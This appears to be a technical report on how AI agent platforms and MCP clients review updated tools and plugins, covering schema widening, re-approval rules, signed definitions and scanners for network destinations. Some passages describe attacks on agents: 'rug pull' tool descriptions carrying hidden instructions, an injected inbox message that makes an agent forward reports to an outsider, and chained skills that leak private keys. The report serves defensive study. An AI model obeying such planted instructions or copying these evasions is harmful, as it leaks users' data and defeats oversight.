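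OpenAI bans ads from plugins, but a comparison of tool definitions wouldn't reveal a breach, because an operator can add ads to a tool's results without changing its definition. In *Ads for Agents*, Pouryousef, Montazer and colleagues (2026) queried public MCP servers and found ads in the results of 226. Ads were rare, with evidence of them on only 0.57% of the servers that answered. Of the 6,499 ad links they examined, 64.9% hid their destination, most often behind a redirect on the operator's own host. Someone checking the domain of such a redirect would see the operator's address and nothing suspicious.

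### Server changes take effect before the scan

The main gap in this system, which OpenAI acknowledges, is that OpenAI keeps the tool definition but no copy of the server's code, and changes to the server take effect before a scan can discover or approve them. Because scans run daily, a changed definition can go unnoticed for about a day.

For honest developers, this is mostly a compatibility problem. While OpenAI holds the new definition of `search` for review, the model keeps using the old one, but its calls run the new code. If that code now requires a folder, the search fails. OpenAI tells developers to keep the server compatible with the live definition, and to roll back a change that breaks compatibility instead of waiting for review.

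Holding a tool definition limits what the agent is told to send to the server, but not what the server's code does with the data. Suppose that on Monday the operator of the invoice server adds `notes` to `record_invoice` and also starts copying every invoice to another company. On Tuesday the scan finds `notes` and the checks hold it. The agent isn't told about the new argument, so it doesn't send the user's mail that would have gone there. But the server has been copying invoices since Monday and continues to do so.

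If the operator doesn't add `notes`, the scan finds no difference. OpenAI intends this, and its rules don't require a scan for a change to the server alone if the published definitions still hold. Checking server changes too would be burdensome, because OpenAI would need every server's source code, and proof that the running server used it, before an operator could fix a bug. Without that code and proof, detecting a change behind an unchanged definition requires testing or monitoring the running server.

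OpenAI's reviewers can test the server before the plugin is first published. The submission guide requires the developer to supply five test cases in which the plugin should act, three in which it shouldn't, a video, and a demo account with sample data if users have to sign in. These tests can expose a tool that does something visibly different from its description. They are less likely to catch deliberate deception, because the developer writes the test cases and can program the server to recognize the demo account. OpenAI doesn't say that the daily scan repeats these tests.

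OpenAI also reviews reports from users, and its whitepaper says that it can immediately disable a malicious app, remove it from the directory and notify the administrators of affected companies.

### When a person looks at a held change

Under continuous review, a developer who wants a person to review a held change selects "Appeal" beside the finding and explains why it is wrong. OpenAI's review team then considers all the tool changes held in that scan together. Automatic updates to the server's tools pause during the appeal, so the developer must withdraw it before shipping another change. OpenAI advises that if the finding is valid, fixing the server and rescanning is usually faster.

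These appeals don't cover the plugin's package, its authentication or the server's shared instructions. If the review team rejects a whole submission, the developer appeals by replying to the rejection email.

Reviewers therefore see the changes that an automated check has held and that the developer is willing to defend. A change that passes the check can reach users without a reviewer reading it, however much access it adds. A reviewer may also never see a held change if the developer rewords it until it passes.

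An attacker has little reason to appeal, because the portal shows what the checks found and the attacker can edit the description and request another scan. For a held tool, OpenAI doesn't describe a block like the one Anthropic imposes after a failed security scan, so the attacker could keep trying until a version passes. The success rate would depend on the recall of OpenAI's checks, which its documentation doesn't give.

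## Updates to 39 tool servers: when a compatible change widens permissions

Desktop Commander is an MCP server that lets an agent run commands on the user's computer. In version 0.1.34, its tool `execute_command` accepted two arguments, `command` and `timeout_ms`, and rejected any others. Version 0.1.35 added `shell`, which accepts any text. The change was backward compatible, since every call that worked before still worked, but it let the agent choose which program interprets the command. If a company had allowed only commands that it considered safe in one interpreter, it could no longer rely on that rule, because another interpreter may treat the same text differently.

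*SchemaCaps* (Ameur, Bouzefrane and Banerjee, 2026) examines 604 releases of 39 public MCP servers for changes like this and gives a rule for deciding which changes a person should approve again. Its counts give some idea of how much work a directory would take on if it held every tool whose input schema widens.

### Old calls and new values

Write [S] for the set of calls that an input schema S accepts. If an update replaces S with S′, the change is backward compatible when

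[S] ⊆ [S′]

An update is compatible if the new schema accepts every call that the old one accepted. Developers want compatibility because it keeps existing software working. But it doesn't limit what else the new schema accepts, so a compatible update can let a tool send reports to any address when it could previously send them only to the team's.

The condition that Ameur and colleagues propose concerns arguments that carry authority. An argument carries authority if its value can change what the tool acts on, where data goes, whose account the tool uses or how something runs. By this test `shell` carries authority, and so does the address of a webhook (a web address to which a service sends results). A search filter or a page-size limit doesn't. Let K be the set of arguments that carry authority, and let π_K[S] be all the combinations of values they can take in calls that S accepts. The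 change is non-amplifying when

π_K[S′] ⊆ π_K[S]

so that no combination becomes possible that wasn't possible before.

Arguments that the agent leaves out also need a value. This is the schema's default if there is one, and otherwise ⊥, which means the server chooses. In Desktop Commander 0.1.34, a call containing `shell` was invalid, so the only possible value of `shell` was ⊥. In 0.1.35 it could be any text. The update is compatible because every call that was valid in 0.1.34 remained valid, but it is also amplifying because `shell` could now take values other than ⊥.

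A change can have either property without the other:

| | No new value on an argument that carries authority | A new value on such an argument |
|---|---|---|
| **Old calls still work** | A search tool gains an optional page-size limit | `execute_command` gains an optional `shell` |
| **Some old calls fail** | An optional destination becomes required | A tool gains a required destination |

Under this definition, a server could gain a practical ability without counting as amplifying if its first approved version accepted undeclared fields, as JSON Schema objects do unless their author forbids it. Such a schema already accepts a field called `shell` with any value, so declaring `shell` in a later version doesn't expand what the schema accepts. But an agent learns from the schema which arguments exist, and would have had little reason to send `shell` before it was declared. If the approved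 version rejected undeclared fields, a server can't get around the condition by first accepting them and then declaring one, because accepting them is itself an amplification.

### The re-approval rule, step by step

The rule runs in the client, the part of an AI application that connects to MCP servers. When a user approves a tool, the client records the server's identity and a fingerprint of the input schema. When the server publishes a new definition, the client makes these checks in order and suspends the tool at the first failure:

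1. **Server identity.** The launch command and the server's reported name must match the approved ones.
2. **The client's list of harmless arguments.** The client may keep a list of arguments that carry no authority. Adding an already approved argument to that list requires a new approval.
3. **Behaviour labels.** The tool fails if the server stops labelling it read-only, or starts labelling it destructive or open-world.
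4. **Identical schema.** If the input schema is the same, the tool stays approved and the remaining checks don't apply, even if the description is new.
5. **Linked arguments.** If the old schema contains conditions that link arguments to each other, checking the arguments one by one isn't reliable, so the tool fails.
6. **Structural changes.** The tool fails if an object that rejected undeclared fields gains a new one or starts accepting them. It also fails if an argument becomes optional, accepts null for the first time, gets a different default, or disappears after being required or having a default.
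7. **Values.** For each argument, the old schema must have accepted every value that the new one accepts. If the client can't tell, the tool fails.

Checks 6 and 7 skip the arguments on the client's list. If the tool passes, the client records the new schema as approved. If it fails, the client hides the tool from the model until a person approves the version, restricts what the tool may do, or refuses it. The client also makes the tool available again if a later release stays within the schema that the user had approved, so a developer can undo a widening without needing anyone's approval.

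The fifth check catches changes that are missed when each argument is checked separately. Suppose a tool requires either `id` or `full_path`, and an update requires neither. Each argument could already be absent, so checking them separately finds no new value. But a call can now omit both, which lets the server choose the target. Conditions that link arguments were rare in the servers studied, with only 20 cases that the client couldn't decide. They may become more common because the July 2026 revision of the Model Context Protocol lets input schemas use any keyword from the current JSON Schema standard.

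The client's list of arguments that carry no authority is empty by default, so the client treats every argument as if it carried authority. A malicious developer gains nothing by giving a dangerous argument an innocent name. In the invented invoice plugin, the default rule suspends `record_invoice` if it gains a free-text argument, `notes`. But Ameur and colleagues class free content as carrying no authority, so a client that followed their criterion would put `notes` on its list and allow the change, despite the risk to private mail. The rule doesn't cover the plugin's new scope and new domain, because they aren't in the input schema.

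The check on behaviour labels catches changes in only one direction, so a server can relabel a destructive tool as read-only and still pass, even though the new label may remove a confirmation prompt. A client that adopted the rule would be safer if it suspended the tool after any label change.

Comparing values is hard because no program can decide for every pair of JSON Schemas whether one accepts everything that the other does. Ameur and colleagues took an existing checker and added a correction and a short random search for counterexamples. They tested it on 600 generated pairs of schemas, 314 of which should have failed. The original checker wrongly passed 37 of the 314, and the improved one passed none. A similar test of the whole rule found that an earlier version let through 27 of 330 amplifying changes. Of these, 24 removed a required argument or one with a default, which leaves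 its value to the server. Ameur and colleagues have fixed both errors that the test exposed, and the current rule let none of the changes through. This is good evidence for the rule, but the schemas were small and artificial, and a real server could still contain a case that the tests didn't cover.

### What changed in 604 releases

The study covered MCP servers that run on the user's machine. These were the official reference servers and, from the large package registry npm, the 15 most downloaded third-party servers that list their tools without a real login. For each server, Ameur and colleagues took up to 20 stable releases published between January 2025 and September 2026. They installed each release with the dependencies available on its publication date, started it and requested its tool definitions. Of 657 releases, 604 returned definitions, which gave 565 pairs of successive releases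 to compare.

| | Official servers | Third-party servers | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Pairs of releases | 337 | 228 | 565 |
| Changed input schemas | 87 | 1,110 | 1,197 |
| Backward compatible | 63 | 517 | 580 |
| Compatible, and widening something | 34 | 378 | 412 |

A tool counts once for each pair in which its schema changes. About 71% of the compatible changes widened something, so a reviewer can infer very little about access from a developer's assurance that an update is backward compatible. The most common widenings were a new argument on a closed object (167 changes), a larger range of permitted values (134) and an object that started accepting undeclared fields (129). A single change could include several of these. *MCPEvol-Bench* (2026), which tests how agents cope with server changes, also lists added optional arguments as one of the usual ways servers evolve.

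Many of the 412 changes are harmless additions such as filters. To find the ones that matter, Ameur and colleagues first used a program that classifies arguments by name, and it flagged 84 changes. Two of the authors then separately labelled 176 cases without seeing the program's results, and a third settled their 29 disagreements. They confirmed 66 of the 84 and found 10 that the program had missed, so by their count at least 76 changes added or widened an argument that carries authority. The true number could be higher, because they looked for misses only among newly added arguments. It could be lower if outsiders judged the cases differently, since all three labellers had an interest in the study.

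The program's mistakes show the risk of building a scanner around suspicious names. A quarter of the arguments it flagged carried no authority, and it missed `saveScript` and `webhook.headers`. In a staged test, it also missed an update that widened a `deploy` tool's `env` argument, previously limited to a test environment, because `env` doesn't resemble any name on its list.

Besides `shell`, the confirmed cases include a `webhookUrl` argument in Firecrawl's server, a `regionUrl` in Sentry's and a `target_project_id` in GitLab's. A scanner that looks for new network destinations by comparing the domains in the two versions' files would miss the two URL arguments, because the update adds only the argument and the agent fills in the address later, during a task. All of these arguments have obvious legitimate uses, and the study reports no attack through any of them.

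An honest developer's update can still make someone else's attack possible. Ameur and colleagues set up a server whose `send_report` tool could at first send only to a team address, and they planted a message in its inbox instructing the agent to forward reports to an outsider. Once an update let the tool send to any address, the report went to the outsider, whether the client accepted every update or only the compatible ones. The agent was a short script that always obeyed such messages, so the test doesn't measure how often a real model would.

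### Why 76 changes don't give a general rate

The 84 changes that the program flagged came from only 6 servers and 20 pairs of releases. Two packages accounted for 62 of them. In one, a server for automating mobile phones, 37 tools gained the same two arguments for local file paths. In the other, an error-tracking server, 15 tools gained an argument for a regional address.

The 84 are 14.5% of the compatible changes. When Ameur and colleagues repeatedly resampled the packages at random, that share ranged from 3.5% to 25.2%. They warn that this range describes how stable their figures are, not the wider population of servers. The sample consists of official and popular servers that run locally and excludes remote servers.

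Kraishan (2026), in *Same Name, Different Server*, examined a far larger group, all 21,643 servers in the official MCP registry in August 2026. But none of the registry's 72,606 version records contains a tool definition, so nobody can use it to count widened schemas. Among the 8,900 servers with several versions, 40.6% had changed a description, an address or something similar while every identifier stayed the same. Most of these servers had reworded their registry description, which need not affect access.

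A smaller group in the census, 370 servers (4.2%), had kept their names but moved their remote address to a different host. Kraishan thinks most were routine migrations, but neither the registry nor a client could distinguish a migration from a takeover. He recommends that clients record the host they first connected to and ask the user before following a server to a new one. OpenAI's directory goes further and requires developers who change hosts to repeat the review. For other clients, recording the host would take little effort and interrupt few people.

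### Fingerprints and rug pulls

Pinning a tool definition is simpler than reasoning about its schema, because the client only has to stop when the definition's fingerprint no longer matches the approved one. The fingerprint doesn't show what changed, so the client must also keep the old text to show the user the difference. The fingerprint also detects changes only in the fields it covers, so one computed from the description alone would miss a new argument.

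In April 2025, the security company Invariant Labs recommended pinning as a defence against what it called a rug pull. Its *MCP Security Notification* (2025) describes a malicious server that waits until the user has approved a tool, then rewrites the tool's description to include harmful instructions. The model reads the new description, but the user may never see it. *MCP-38* (Shen, Toyoda and Leung, 2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, uses the term more broadly, grouping rug pulls with changes in a tool's behaviour. A fingerprint catches such a change only if the tool's definition changes too.

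Ameur and colleagues counted how often each rule would have required a new approval for tools present in both releases of a pair:

| Rule | Re-approvals | What it lets through |
|---|---|---|
| Pin the whole definition | 2,004 | New behaviour behind an identical definition |
| Pin the input schema | 1,197 | New behaviour behind an identical schema; rewritten descriptions |
| Ameur and colleagues' rule | 645 | New behaviour behind an identical or narrower schema; rewritten descriptions |
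| Require backward compatibility | 617 | All 412 compatible widenings; rewritten descriptions; new behaviour behind a compatible schema |

Of the 2,004 re-approvals, 807 were for changes to a description or title alone. Skipping these saves a great deal of work but misses the rug pull in Invariant Labs' original sense, which needs only a new description. A client that used the study's rule would need another way to inspect descriptions, such as a language model that looks for hidden instructions. Pinning the whole definition requires no such inspection, and the extra interruptions may be worth it for a server that handles payroll or production systems.

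The totals of 645 and 617 are close, but they cover different changes. A compatibility rule stops updates that break old calls, which users would probably notice anyway. The study's rule lets at least 323 of those updates through because they only narrow what the tool accepts, and it stops all 412 of the widenings that the compatibility rule misses. Reviewers answer 28 more questions under the study's rule, but it makes much better use of their time.

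Simpler versions of the rule work less well. If the client relied on the program that judges arguments by name, it would need only 413 re-approvals but would miss whatever the program misses. If it required only that the new schema accept no call that the old one rejected, it would need 693 re-approvals and still miss 7 amplifying changes, because that test ignores defaults.

These counts exclude new tools. Every rule requires approval for a new tool, and the releases added 907. Under the study's rule, that makes 1,552 approvals, more than half of them for new tools, so even a perfect rule for changed schemas would leave most of the approvals in place. The counts are also per tool. A client could show the phone-automation server's 37 identical changes as one question, which would reduce interruptions without weakening the check. We don't know whether users would think most of the questions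 necessary, and Ameur and colleagues expect that 645 of them would invite rubber-stamping.

### New behaviour behind the same definition

Every rule in the comparison failed when the staged server kept its schema and changed what its code did. Real servers also change this way. In *When Valid Tool Calls Change Meaning*, Kim and Kang (2026) ran pairs of releases with matching definitions and sent both releases the same call. An older release of the official Git server treated one argument as an option for the Git program and created a file that it shouldn't have. An older release of DBHub, a database server, altered a database that was supposed to be read-only. Later releases of both servers rejected the calls.

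Both of these updates made the server safer, so pinning has a drawback even when it works, because a user who pins an exact release also keeps its security holes. The danger in these cases comes from returning to an older version, for example when an operator undoes a faulty release. Kim and Kang found another case in GitHub's server. If the agent doesn't specify whether a new repository should be private, version 1.4.0 makes it private and version 1.3.0 makes it public. In their test deployment, a model wrote its call after reading the 1.4 definition, but the operator rolled the server back before the call ran, so the call became a request for a public repository. Here the definitions do differ, so a client that checked the definition again just before the call could have caught the mismatch.

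When a tool's definition is identical in both releases, Kim and Kang check the source code. Their system works out what a given call would do in the next release and lets it proceed only if the effect stays within what the user approved. In a test with six waiting calls, three would have had the same private effect in the new release and three would have become public. The system completed the first three and blocked the others. Pinning the exact release stopped all six, while approving the release as a whole let all six through. Checking the source code is the most precise of the methods, but it requires the official code and an expert's description of each server's structure, and neither is available for a remote server whose operator keeps the code private.

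### What eight clients and scanners do

In September 2026, Ameur and colleagues examined how eight products respond when an approved tool's permissions widen. They built a test server whose `read_file` tool drops a restriction and gains a `webhookUrl` mid-session, while its name and description stay the same. They ran four products against it, read the source code of one, and relied on documentation for the other three.

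| Product | Response to the wider schema | Evidence |
|---|---|---|
| MCP TypeScript and Python developer kits | They send the wider call without comparing definitions | Tests and source code |
| Vercel AI SDK, a developer kit | The same by default; an optional check reports any change | Tests and source code |
| VS Code's agent mode | Approval depends on the tool's name, so it survives the change | Source code |
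| Claude Code | It fetches the new definition, and its permission rules match tool names | Documentation |
| Claude Desktop and Cursor | Unknown | Documentation |
| mcp-scan, a security scanner | No warning | Tests and source code |

None of the six products with a known response required a new approval. This is more worrying for VS Code and Claude Code than for the three developer kits, which have no user to ask. An application built with one of the kits can add its own check, but its developer has to know that the check is missing, and all three kits continue without one by default.

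Under the July 2026 revision of the Model Context Protocol, a server notifies a client of changed tools only if the client has subscribed to those notices. Otherwise the client gets the changes when it next fetches the tool list, and the server suggests how long the client may keep the old list. The revision doesn't require the client to compare the new list with the old one or ask the user about any differences.

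The scanner's result is surprising because Invariant Labs built mcp-scan partly to catch rug pulls. Invariant Labs' *Introducing MCP-Scan* (2025), published ten days after the company's warning, advertised "Tool Pinning" that would detect changes by fingerprinting tools. The fingerprint covered only the description, so the scanner could catch a rewritten description but not a new `shell` argument added while the description stayed the same. Invariant Labs' *Issue Code Reference* is consistent with this, since it ties the warning "Entity has changed" to the tool's description.

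According to Ameur and colleagues, mcp-scan's developers removed even that check in version 0.4.6, so anyone who relied on it to notice changes lost that protection by upgrading. The scanner now belongs to the security company Snyk and is called Agent Scan. In May 2026, Snyk's guide to it listed checks for prompt injection, malware and risky combinations of tools, but none for changed definitions.

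### Signed definitions: ETDI and later proposals

A fingerprint in the client can't show who made a change. Bhatt, Narajala and Habler (2025), in *ETDI*, proposed adding signatures to the protocol for this purpose. Under their Enhanced Tool Definition Interface, a tool's provider signs the complete definition, including its version number and the permissions it needs, and must issue a new signed version after any change. The client then proceeds as follows:

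1. It verifies the signature and rejects the tool if the signature is invalid.
2. If the user has never approved the tool, it asks for approval.
3. If the version number is higher than the approved one, it asks again.
4. If the version number is the same but the fingerprint differs, it records possible tampering and asks again.
5. If the version number is lower, it records a warning and follows whatever policy the client has for old versions.
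6. After approval, it stores the version, the fingerprint and the permissions.

The signature protects against an outsider who alters a definition on its way to the user or imitates a well-known provider. It does little against a rug pull by the provider, who holds the key and can sign a malicious version. The new approval helps in that case, and ETDI requires one for every new version, so its workload would resemble that of pinning whole definitions. The open policy on old versions also deserves more attention than it gets in the proposal, given what Kim and Kang later found about rollbacks.

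Bhatt and colleagues describe a wallpaper tool whose provider secretly changes the server's code to search the user's documents for financial information and upload them. The tool keeps its name and version number. ETDI would not detect this if the provider left the tool's definition unchanged. To address this, ETDI allows a definition to include a fingerprint of the server's API contract, the formal description of the requests it accepts and the responses it gives. But the tool can start reading documents without accepting any new request, which leaves the contract unchanged.

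Bhatt and colleagues foresaw obstacles to adoption. Providers would have to manage signing keys, clients would have to build approval screens that people understand, and neither side would benefit much until the other took part. The *Model Context Protocol Python SDK with ETDI Security* is a working implementation, but the protocol hasn't adopted the idea. In May 2026 the Model Context Protocol's *Specification Enhancement Proposals (SEPs)* listed 36 accepted or final proposals, none about signing or pinning tool definitions, and the July revision added neither.

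*MCPS* (Sharif, 2026) proposes signing the whole tool definition, signing messages, and verifying agents' identities. Sharif submitted it in March 2026 as an Internet-Draft, a working document that anyone can send to the body that standardizes internet protocols, and a second version followed in August. *Attested Tool-Server Admission* (Metere, 2026) focuses on which servers and tools a client should admit in the first place. It leaves monitoring for later changes to separate software, and Ameur and colleagues designed their rule for that kind of monitoring.

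A signature or a local fingerprint also can't reveal that a server gives different users different definitions. *Characterizing Network Centralization and Observability in the Remote MCP Ecosystem* (2026) suggests a public log of tool schemas that servers could add to but nobody could delete from, like the existing logs for website certificates. A company could then check that the schema it received matches the public one, and anyone could look up when a tool gained an argument. The suggestion has no detailed specification yet.

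## Finding network destinations in plugin code: Dify, DefenseClaw and a study of skills

A tool definition doesn't show where the tool's code sends data, but if the code ships with the plugin, a scanner can search it for addresses.

### Building a list of domains

A scanner can build the list in these steps:

1. Read any domains that the author declares in the manifest.
2. Extract addresses from the scripts, settings files and written instructions.
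3. Identify the outside packages that the plugin installs and, if possible, search those too.
4. Compare the result with the author's declaration, an allowlist or the domains in the approved version.

Extraction is easy or hard depending on how the author wrote the code. Here are three ways for a script in the invoice plugin to upload a PDF to the outside converter:

```
post("https://convert.invoice-tools.example/pdf", file)
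post("https://" + settings["converter"] + "/pdf", file)
invoice_sdk.convert(file)
```

A search for web addresses finds the domain in the first line. The second line gets the domain from a settings file, which may exist only on the user's machine. The third line has no address because the conversion company's own package supplies it.

A text search also finds addresses that the plugin never contacts, such as links in a README. SkillFortify, the scanner in *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (2026), deliberately treats any web address in a skill as evidence that the skill can read from the network, and any HTTP method for sending or changing data as evidence that it can write. This is a cautious way to infer network access, but a reviewer looking for new destinations would have to sort through many harmless links.

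A more precise scanner traces each address to the code that makes the request, which requires it to parse the programming language. *Auditing MCP Servers for Over-Privileged Tool Capabilities* (2026) tested a scanner on nine deliberately vulnerable servers. Its static scan flagged both Python servers but none of the seven in JavaScript, because of limits in its parser. A sandbox test detected all seven. The study covered security flaws in general, not hidden domains, but a domain extractor with the same parser would have the same problem. An empty list of domains is therefore reassuring only if the scanner could parse the files.

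The result also depends on the comparison. Suppose version 2 of the invoice plugin adds the PDF converter, and the scanner finds its domain:

| Version 2's domains compared with | Does the scanner report the converter? | What the comparison misses |
|---|---|---|
| The author's declaration | Only if the author left it out | Any destination that the author declares |
| A company's allowlist | Only if the company hasn't already allowed it, perhaps for another plugin | A plugin's first use of a domain on the list |
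| The domains in version 1 | Yes | A domain that version 1 contained but never used |

Comparing versions is the most direct way to find an expansion. But an attacker can put a domain in a comment or an unused function in version 1, so that it isn't new when version 2 starts using it.

### Dify: an optional list of domains

Dify makes a platform for building AI applications, and its marketplace listed 928 plugins at the end of July 2026. According to Dify's *Publish a Plugin to Marketplace*, authors can declare the domains they expect a plugin to contact. For version 2 of the invoice plugin, the entry in the manifest might read:

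```
network:
  domains:
    - api.ledger.example
    - convert.invoice-tools.example
```

Dify explains that static analysis can't find every address that a plugin assembles while it runs or that is hidden inside a vendor's software kit. Plugin authors can declare those destinations to make them visible to reviewers, but the declaration is optional, and the guide doesn't mention blocking undeclared destinations. As with the tool lists in skills, a dishonest author can leave out a domain without penalty.

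Dify's validator extracts outbound domains from the plugin package and runs many other checks. Plugin authors can run it locally before they submit the plugin through a pull request, which starts the automated checks. Blocking errors stop the submission. If there are only warnings, the submission can proceed, but a reviewer may ask the author to explain them or change the plugin. A maintainer then reviews the submission, and Dify validates the package again after merging it.

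The guide doesn't specify which result an author gets if the validator finds a domain that the manifest doesn't declare. Dify's list of common blocking failures includes failing to disclose sensitive capabilities, but not undeclared domains. *Trust Is Not a Badge* (Dify, 2026) says that clear-cut failures should block a plugin and ambiguous signals should begin as warnings. An undeclared domain therefore probably produces a warning, since declaring domains is optional and the validator may have found a harmless link.

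Dify plans to be stricter in the security grades it shows to users. Under the draft scheme, a plugin with "undeclared sensitive external access" would get a C, the lowest grade, with a red badge and a prominent warning before installation. Dify doesn't define "sensitive" there, and in August 2026 it described the grades as still evolving. A grade would apply to only one version, and each upgrade would need a new scan.

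To publish an update, the author raises the version number and opens a pull request with the new package. The package goes through the same checks again, and a maintainer reviews every update, including any that adds a domain. The guide doesn't mention comparing the new version with the earlier one. But Dify tells authors to leave old packages in the public repository, so a reviewer or a customer can extract the domains from both versions and compare them.

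The other disclosures don't necessarily reveal a new destination either. Plugin authors assign each submission a risk level, and medium risk covers plugins that write to an outside service or send user content externally. Version 1 of the invoice plugin is already medium risk because it writes to an accounting system, and adding the converter doesn't change its level. The privacy policy is more useful because it must describe the data that a plugin sends to third parties. Dify also warns authors against reusing an old pull request description for a changed version.

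Dify also tells authors that new versions must add real capability, though it separately encourages updates for bug fixes and security patches. If authors follow the capability rule, many updates will add features, and these will often contact a new domain.

### DefenseClaw: hostnames against an allowlist

DefenseClaw, Cisco's set of security tools for AI agents, includes a scanner that users can run themselves. It inspects plugins for OpenClaw, an agent whose users get skills and plugins from ClawHub. Cisco's *Plugin scanner* describes five analyzers, two of which directly concern access. One checks whether the permissions declared in the plugin's `package.json` file match the code. The other extracts the hostnames the plugin contacts and reports any that are not on an allowlist as `network:unexpected_egress`.

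Cisco gives `manifest:excess_permissions` as an example of a finding but doesn't define "excess". If the manifest requests more permissions than the code uses, the author can remove the extra ones. The problem is more urgent if the code does more than the manifest declares, because an update may have added access without notice.

Cisco says that the network analyzer extracts every hostname the plugin contacts, but a static scan can't guarantee that, for the reasons Dify gives. An optional sandbox run can catch some that it misses. The sandbox loads the plugin and replaces `fetch`, JavaScript's standard function for web requests, with a version that records them. The scan fails if any request goes to a host outside the declared allowlist. The sample configuration limits the run to five seconds, so a plugin that contacts the converter only when an invoice arrives might send nothing in that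 time. The sandbox could also miss requests that don't use `fetch`.

The scanner page doesn't describe a comparison between versions. The allowlist can still help detect new network destinations, because a new hostname produces a finding unless it is on the list.

DefenseClaw's plugin allowlist creates a larger gap. Plugins on the list skip the scan during installation, according to *defenseclaw plugin*, Cisco's reference for the command-line tool. The command that adds a plugin to the list takes a name but no version, so if a company allows version 1 of the invoice plugin and later installs version 2 with the same tool, version 2 appears to skip the scan too. Anthropic's override for Enterprise organizations is safer because it covers only one version. According to Cisco's scanner page, DefenseClaw inspects every plugin directory before OpenClaw loads it, so a later scan may still catch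 the change, but neither page explains how the two rules interact.

DefenseClaw's installation command applies the company's rules for blocking or quarantining plugins only if the user adds the `--action` option, so a scan that finds a problem may not stop the plugin. Cisco says that DefenseClaw doesn't prove a plugin is free of risk and advises pairing it with human review in high-risk deployments.

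### Network access in 6,309 skills

Neither Dify nor Cisco has published how much its scanner misses. The study of skills by Pandey and colleagues gives some idea, because it compares what a static scan found in 6,309 listings with what happened when an agent ran nearly all of them. The listings came from 2,392 publishers and were scanned in July and August 2026.

For the static scan, a Claude model read every file in each listing and recorded the capabilities it found evidence of. Four fixed rules also checked for secrets in the code, downloads that run immediately, invisible characters and unreadable program files. An agent then ran each skill in a sandbox that recorded its processes, tool calls and network requests, and a Google model assessed the recording for most listings. The researchers chose listings for the sandbox without regard to what the static scan had found. Earlier studies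 had run only skills that already looked suspicious, so they couldn't measure access among ordinary ones.

| Capability | Static scan found evidence | Sandbox recorded use |
|---|---|---|
| Shell commands | 50% | 8% |
| Network access | 31% | 5% |
| Credential access | 13% | 5% |
| Writing files | 31% | 41% |

At least 85% of the skills in which the static scan found network access made no recorded request. One session runs few of a skill's paths. The sandbox also had no open connection to the internet, so a script that had to download its settings first may have stopped before contacting anything else.

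The figures for writing files go the other way, probably because the agent often writes files whatever the skill contains.

The two methods also differed in which skills they flagged as risky. At least one reported a risk, such as sensitive data leaving the machine or access beyond what the task needed, in 3,339 listings, but both did so in only 978 of them (29%). The static scan alone flagged 1,653, and the sandbox alone flagged 708. The static scan reported unvetted outside components as a risk in 703 listings and the sandbox in only one, which is unsurprising because an installed package may do nothing during a short test. A company that used only one method would miss many of the risks the other reported, though neither set of reports is a reliable count of real problems.

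Users could see very little of this access in advance, because few authors declared any tools and even fewer declared them accurately. Even the accurate lists left out credentials, because the format has no way to declare access to them. Authors may mention network access in an optional free-text field, but a scanner can't reliably compare prose with code. A list of tools may show that a skill can use the network without showing which domains it contacts.

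Listings on ClawHub included declarations more often than those on skillsmp, but the declarations were less accurate. Among listings with readable frontmatter, 18% declared something on ClawHub, compared with 10% on skillsmp. However, 88% of ClawHub's declarations understated the skill's access, compared with 31% on skillsmp. A marketplace that encourages authors to declare access without checking what they declare may end up with more inaccurate declarations.

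Pandey and colleagues suggest that a marketplace or an independent assessor derive a profile of each skill's access from its files and tie it to the version inspected. Scanners could then compare the profiles of two versions without relying on what the skill's author says. The researchers haven't built such a system, and their study scanned only one version of each skill, so it doesn't show how often updates add network access or a new domain.

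### Destinations that the files don't contain

A destination is often missing from a plugin's code because users set it in the configuration. Many companies host their own copy of a service, so a plugin has to let them enter its address. OpenClaw's *DefenseClaw Security*, a registry page for a plugin that works with DefenseClaw, advises users to install it only if they trust the gateway they configure, and to assume that sensitive activity leaves their machine if that gateway is remote. Users in two companies can therefore install identical files and send data to different places. An update that moves a fixed address into the settings may look like a reduction in access, because a domain disappears from the code.

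The files can also direct the agent to instructions stored elsewhere. Gandhi, Aviv and colleagues (2026), in *Scan Before You Install*, warn that if a skill tells an agent to run commands from a web page, the page's author controls what the agent runs. A scanner can find the page's domain in the skill, but not the domains in commands that the author later adds to the page.

Agents also run commands that aren't in a skill's text. *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action* (2026) compared the commands in skill documents with those that Claude Sonnet 5 ran while following them. In one run with 39 skills, 50 of the agent's 144 commands were of a type that didn't appear in the document, and these came from only 14 of the skills. In another run, only about 3% of the commands matched the document word for word. The sample was deliberately narrow, and the study compared types of command, not domains. Still,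 the results suggest that a scan of a skill's text can't predict everything an agent will do, and that allowing only the exact commands in the text would stop almost all of the agent's work.

Dependencies account for some of the other missing destinations. An Anthropic security plugin for Claude Code installs the company's Agent SDK the first time it runs, which requires network access. The reason is legitimate, but a scanner that reads only the plugin's own files won't find all the code that will run. Pandey and colleagues found 75 listings with a dependency on a host that an outsider might be able to take over. The outsider could then replace the package without adding a domain to the list.

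A server can also pass data on, as DefenseClaw itself does for good reasons. Cisco's *Plugin protocol* explains that DefenseClaw's OpenClaw plugin redirects the agent's requests to language models through a proxy on the user's own machine, adding a header with the original address so the proxy can complete the request. A scanner that records only the immediate destination would find a local address and miss the outside model provider that receives the prompt. A company can inspect this proxy, but it can't inspect a plugin author's remote server.

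Data can also leave through a second plugin. Gandhi and colleagues describe a backup skill that copies private keys into a shared folder and a debugging skill, by a different author, that uploads recent files from that folder to a public site. If an attacker gets the agent to run one after the other, the keys become public without an update to either skill. A scan of each skill would find the folder and the upload site separately, but someone would have to consider both skills together to notice the problem. A plugin that misuses a destination it already had permission to contact also adds no new destination to the list.

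### Ordinary reasons for a new domain

Honest authors frequently add domains, often because a service moves its API to a new host. ClawHub's address is an example. NVIDIA's *Network Policies* documents a sandbox that lets OpenClaw contact only listed hosts and prompts an operator about any other. The list originally had ClawHub at `clawhub.com`, and NVIDIA later changed it to `clawhub.ai`. With the old list, the sandbox would prompt the operator about `clawhub.ai`, even though the operator had already approved the registry under its old address. But the names alone don't show that the same people run both sites, so a reviewer needs outside evidence, such as an announcement at the old address.

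Another common reason is a content delivery network, a group of servers that keeps copies of files close to users so that they load faster. Moving a plugin's images or data files to one adds a domain that may belong to a different company. The network may also use many subdomains, and Dify lets authors declare them all with a wildcard such as `*.cdn.example.com`, which avoids a new finding for each one. The wildcard is riskier if the network lets any customer create a subdomain, because an attacker's subdomain would also match.

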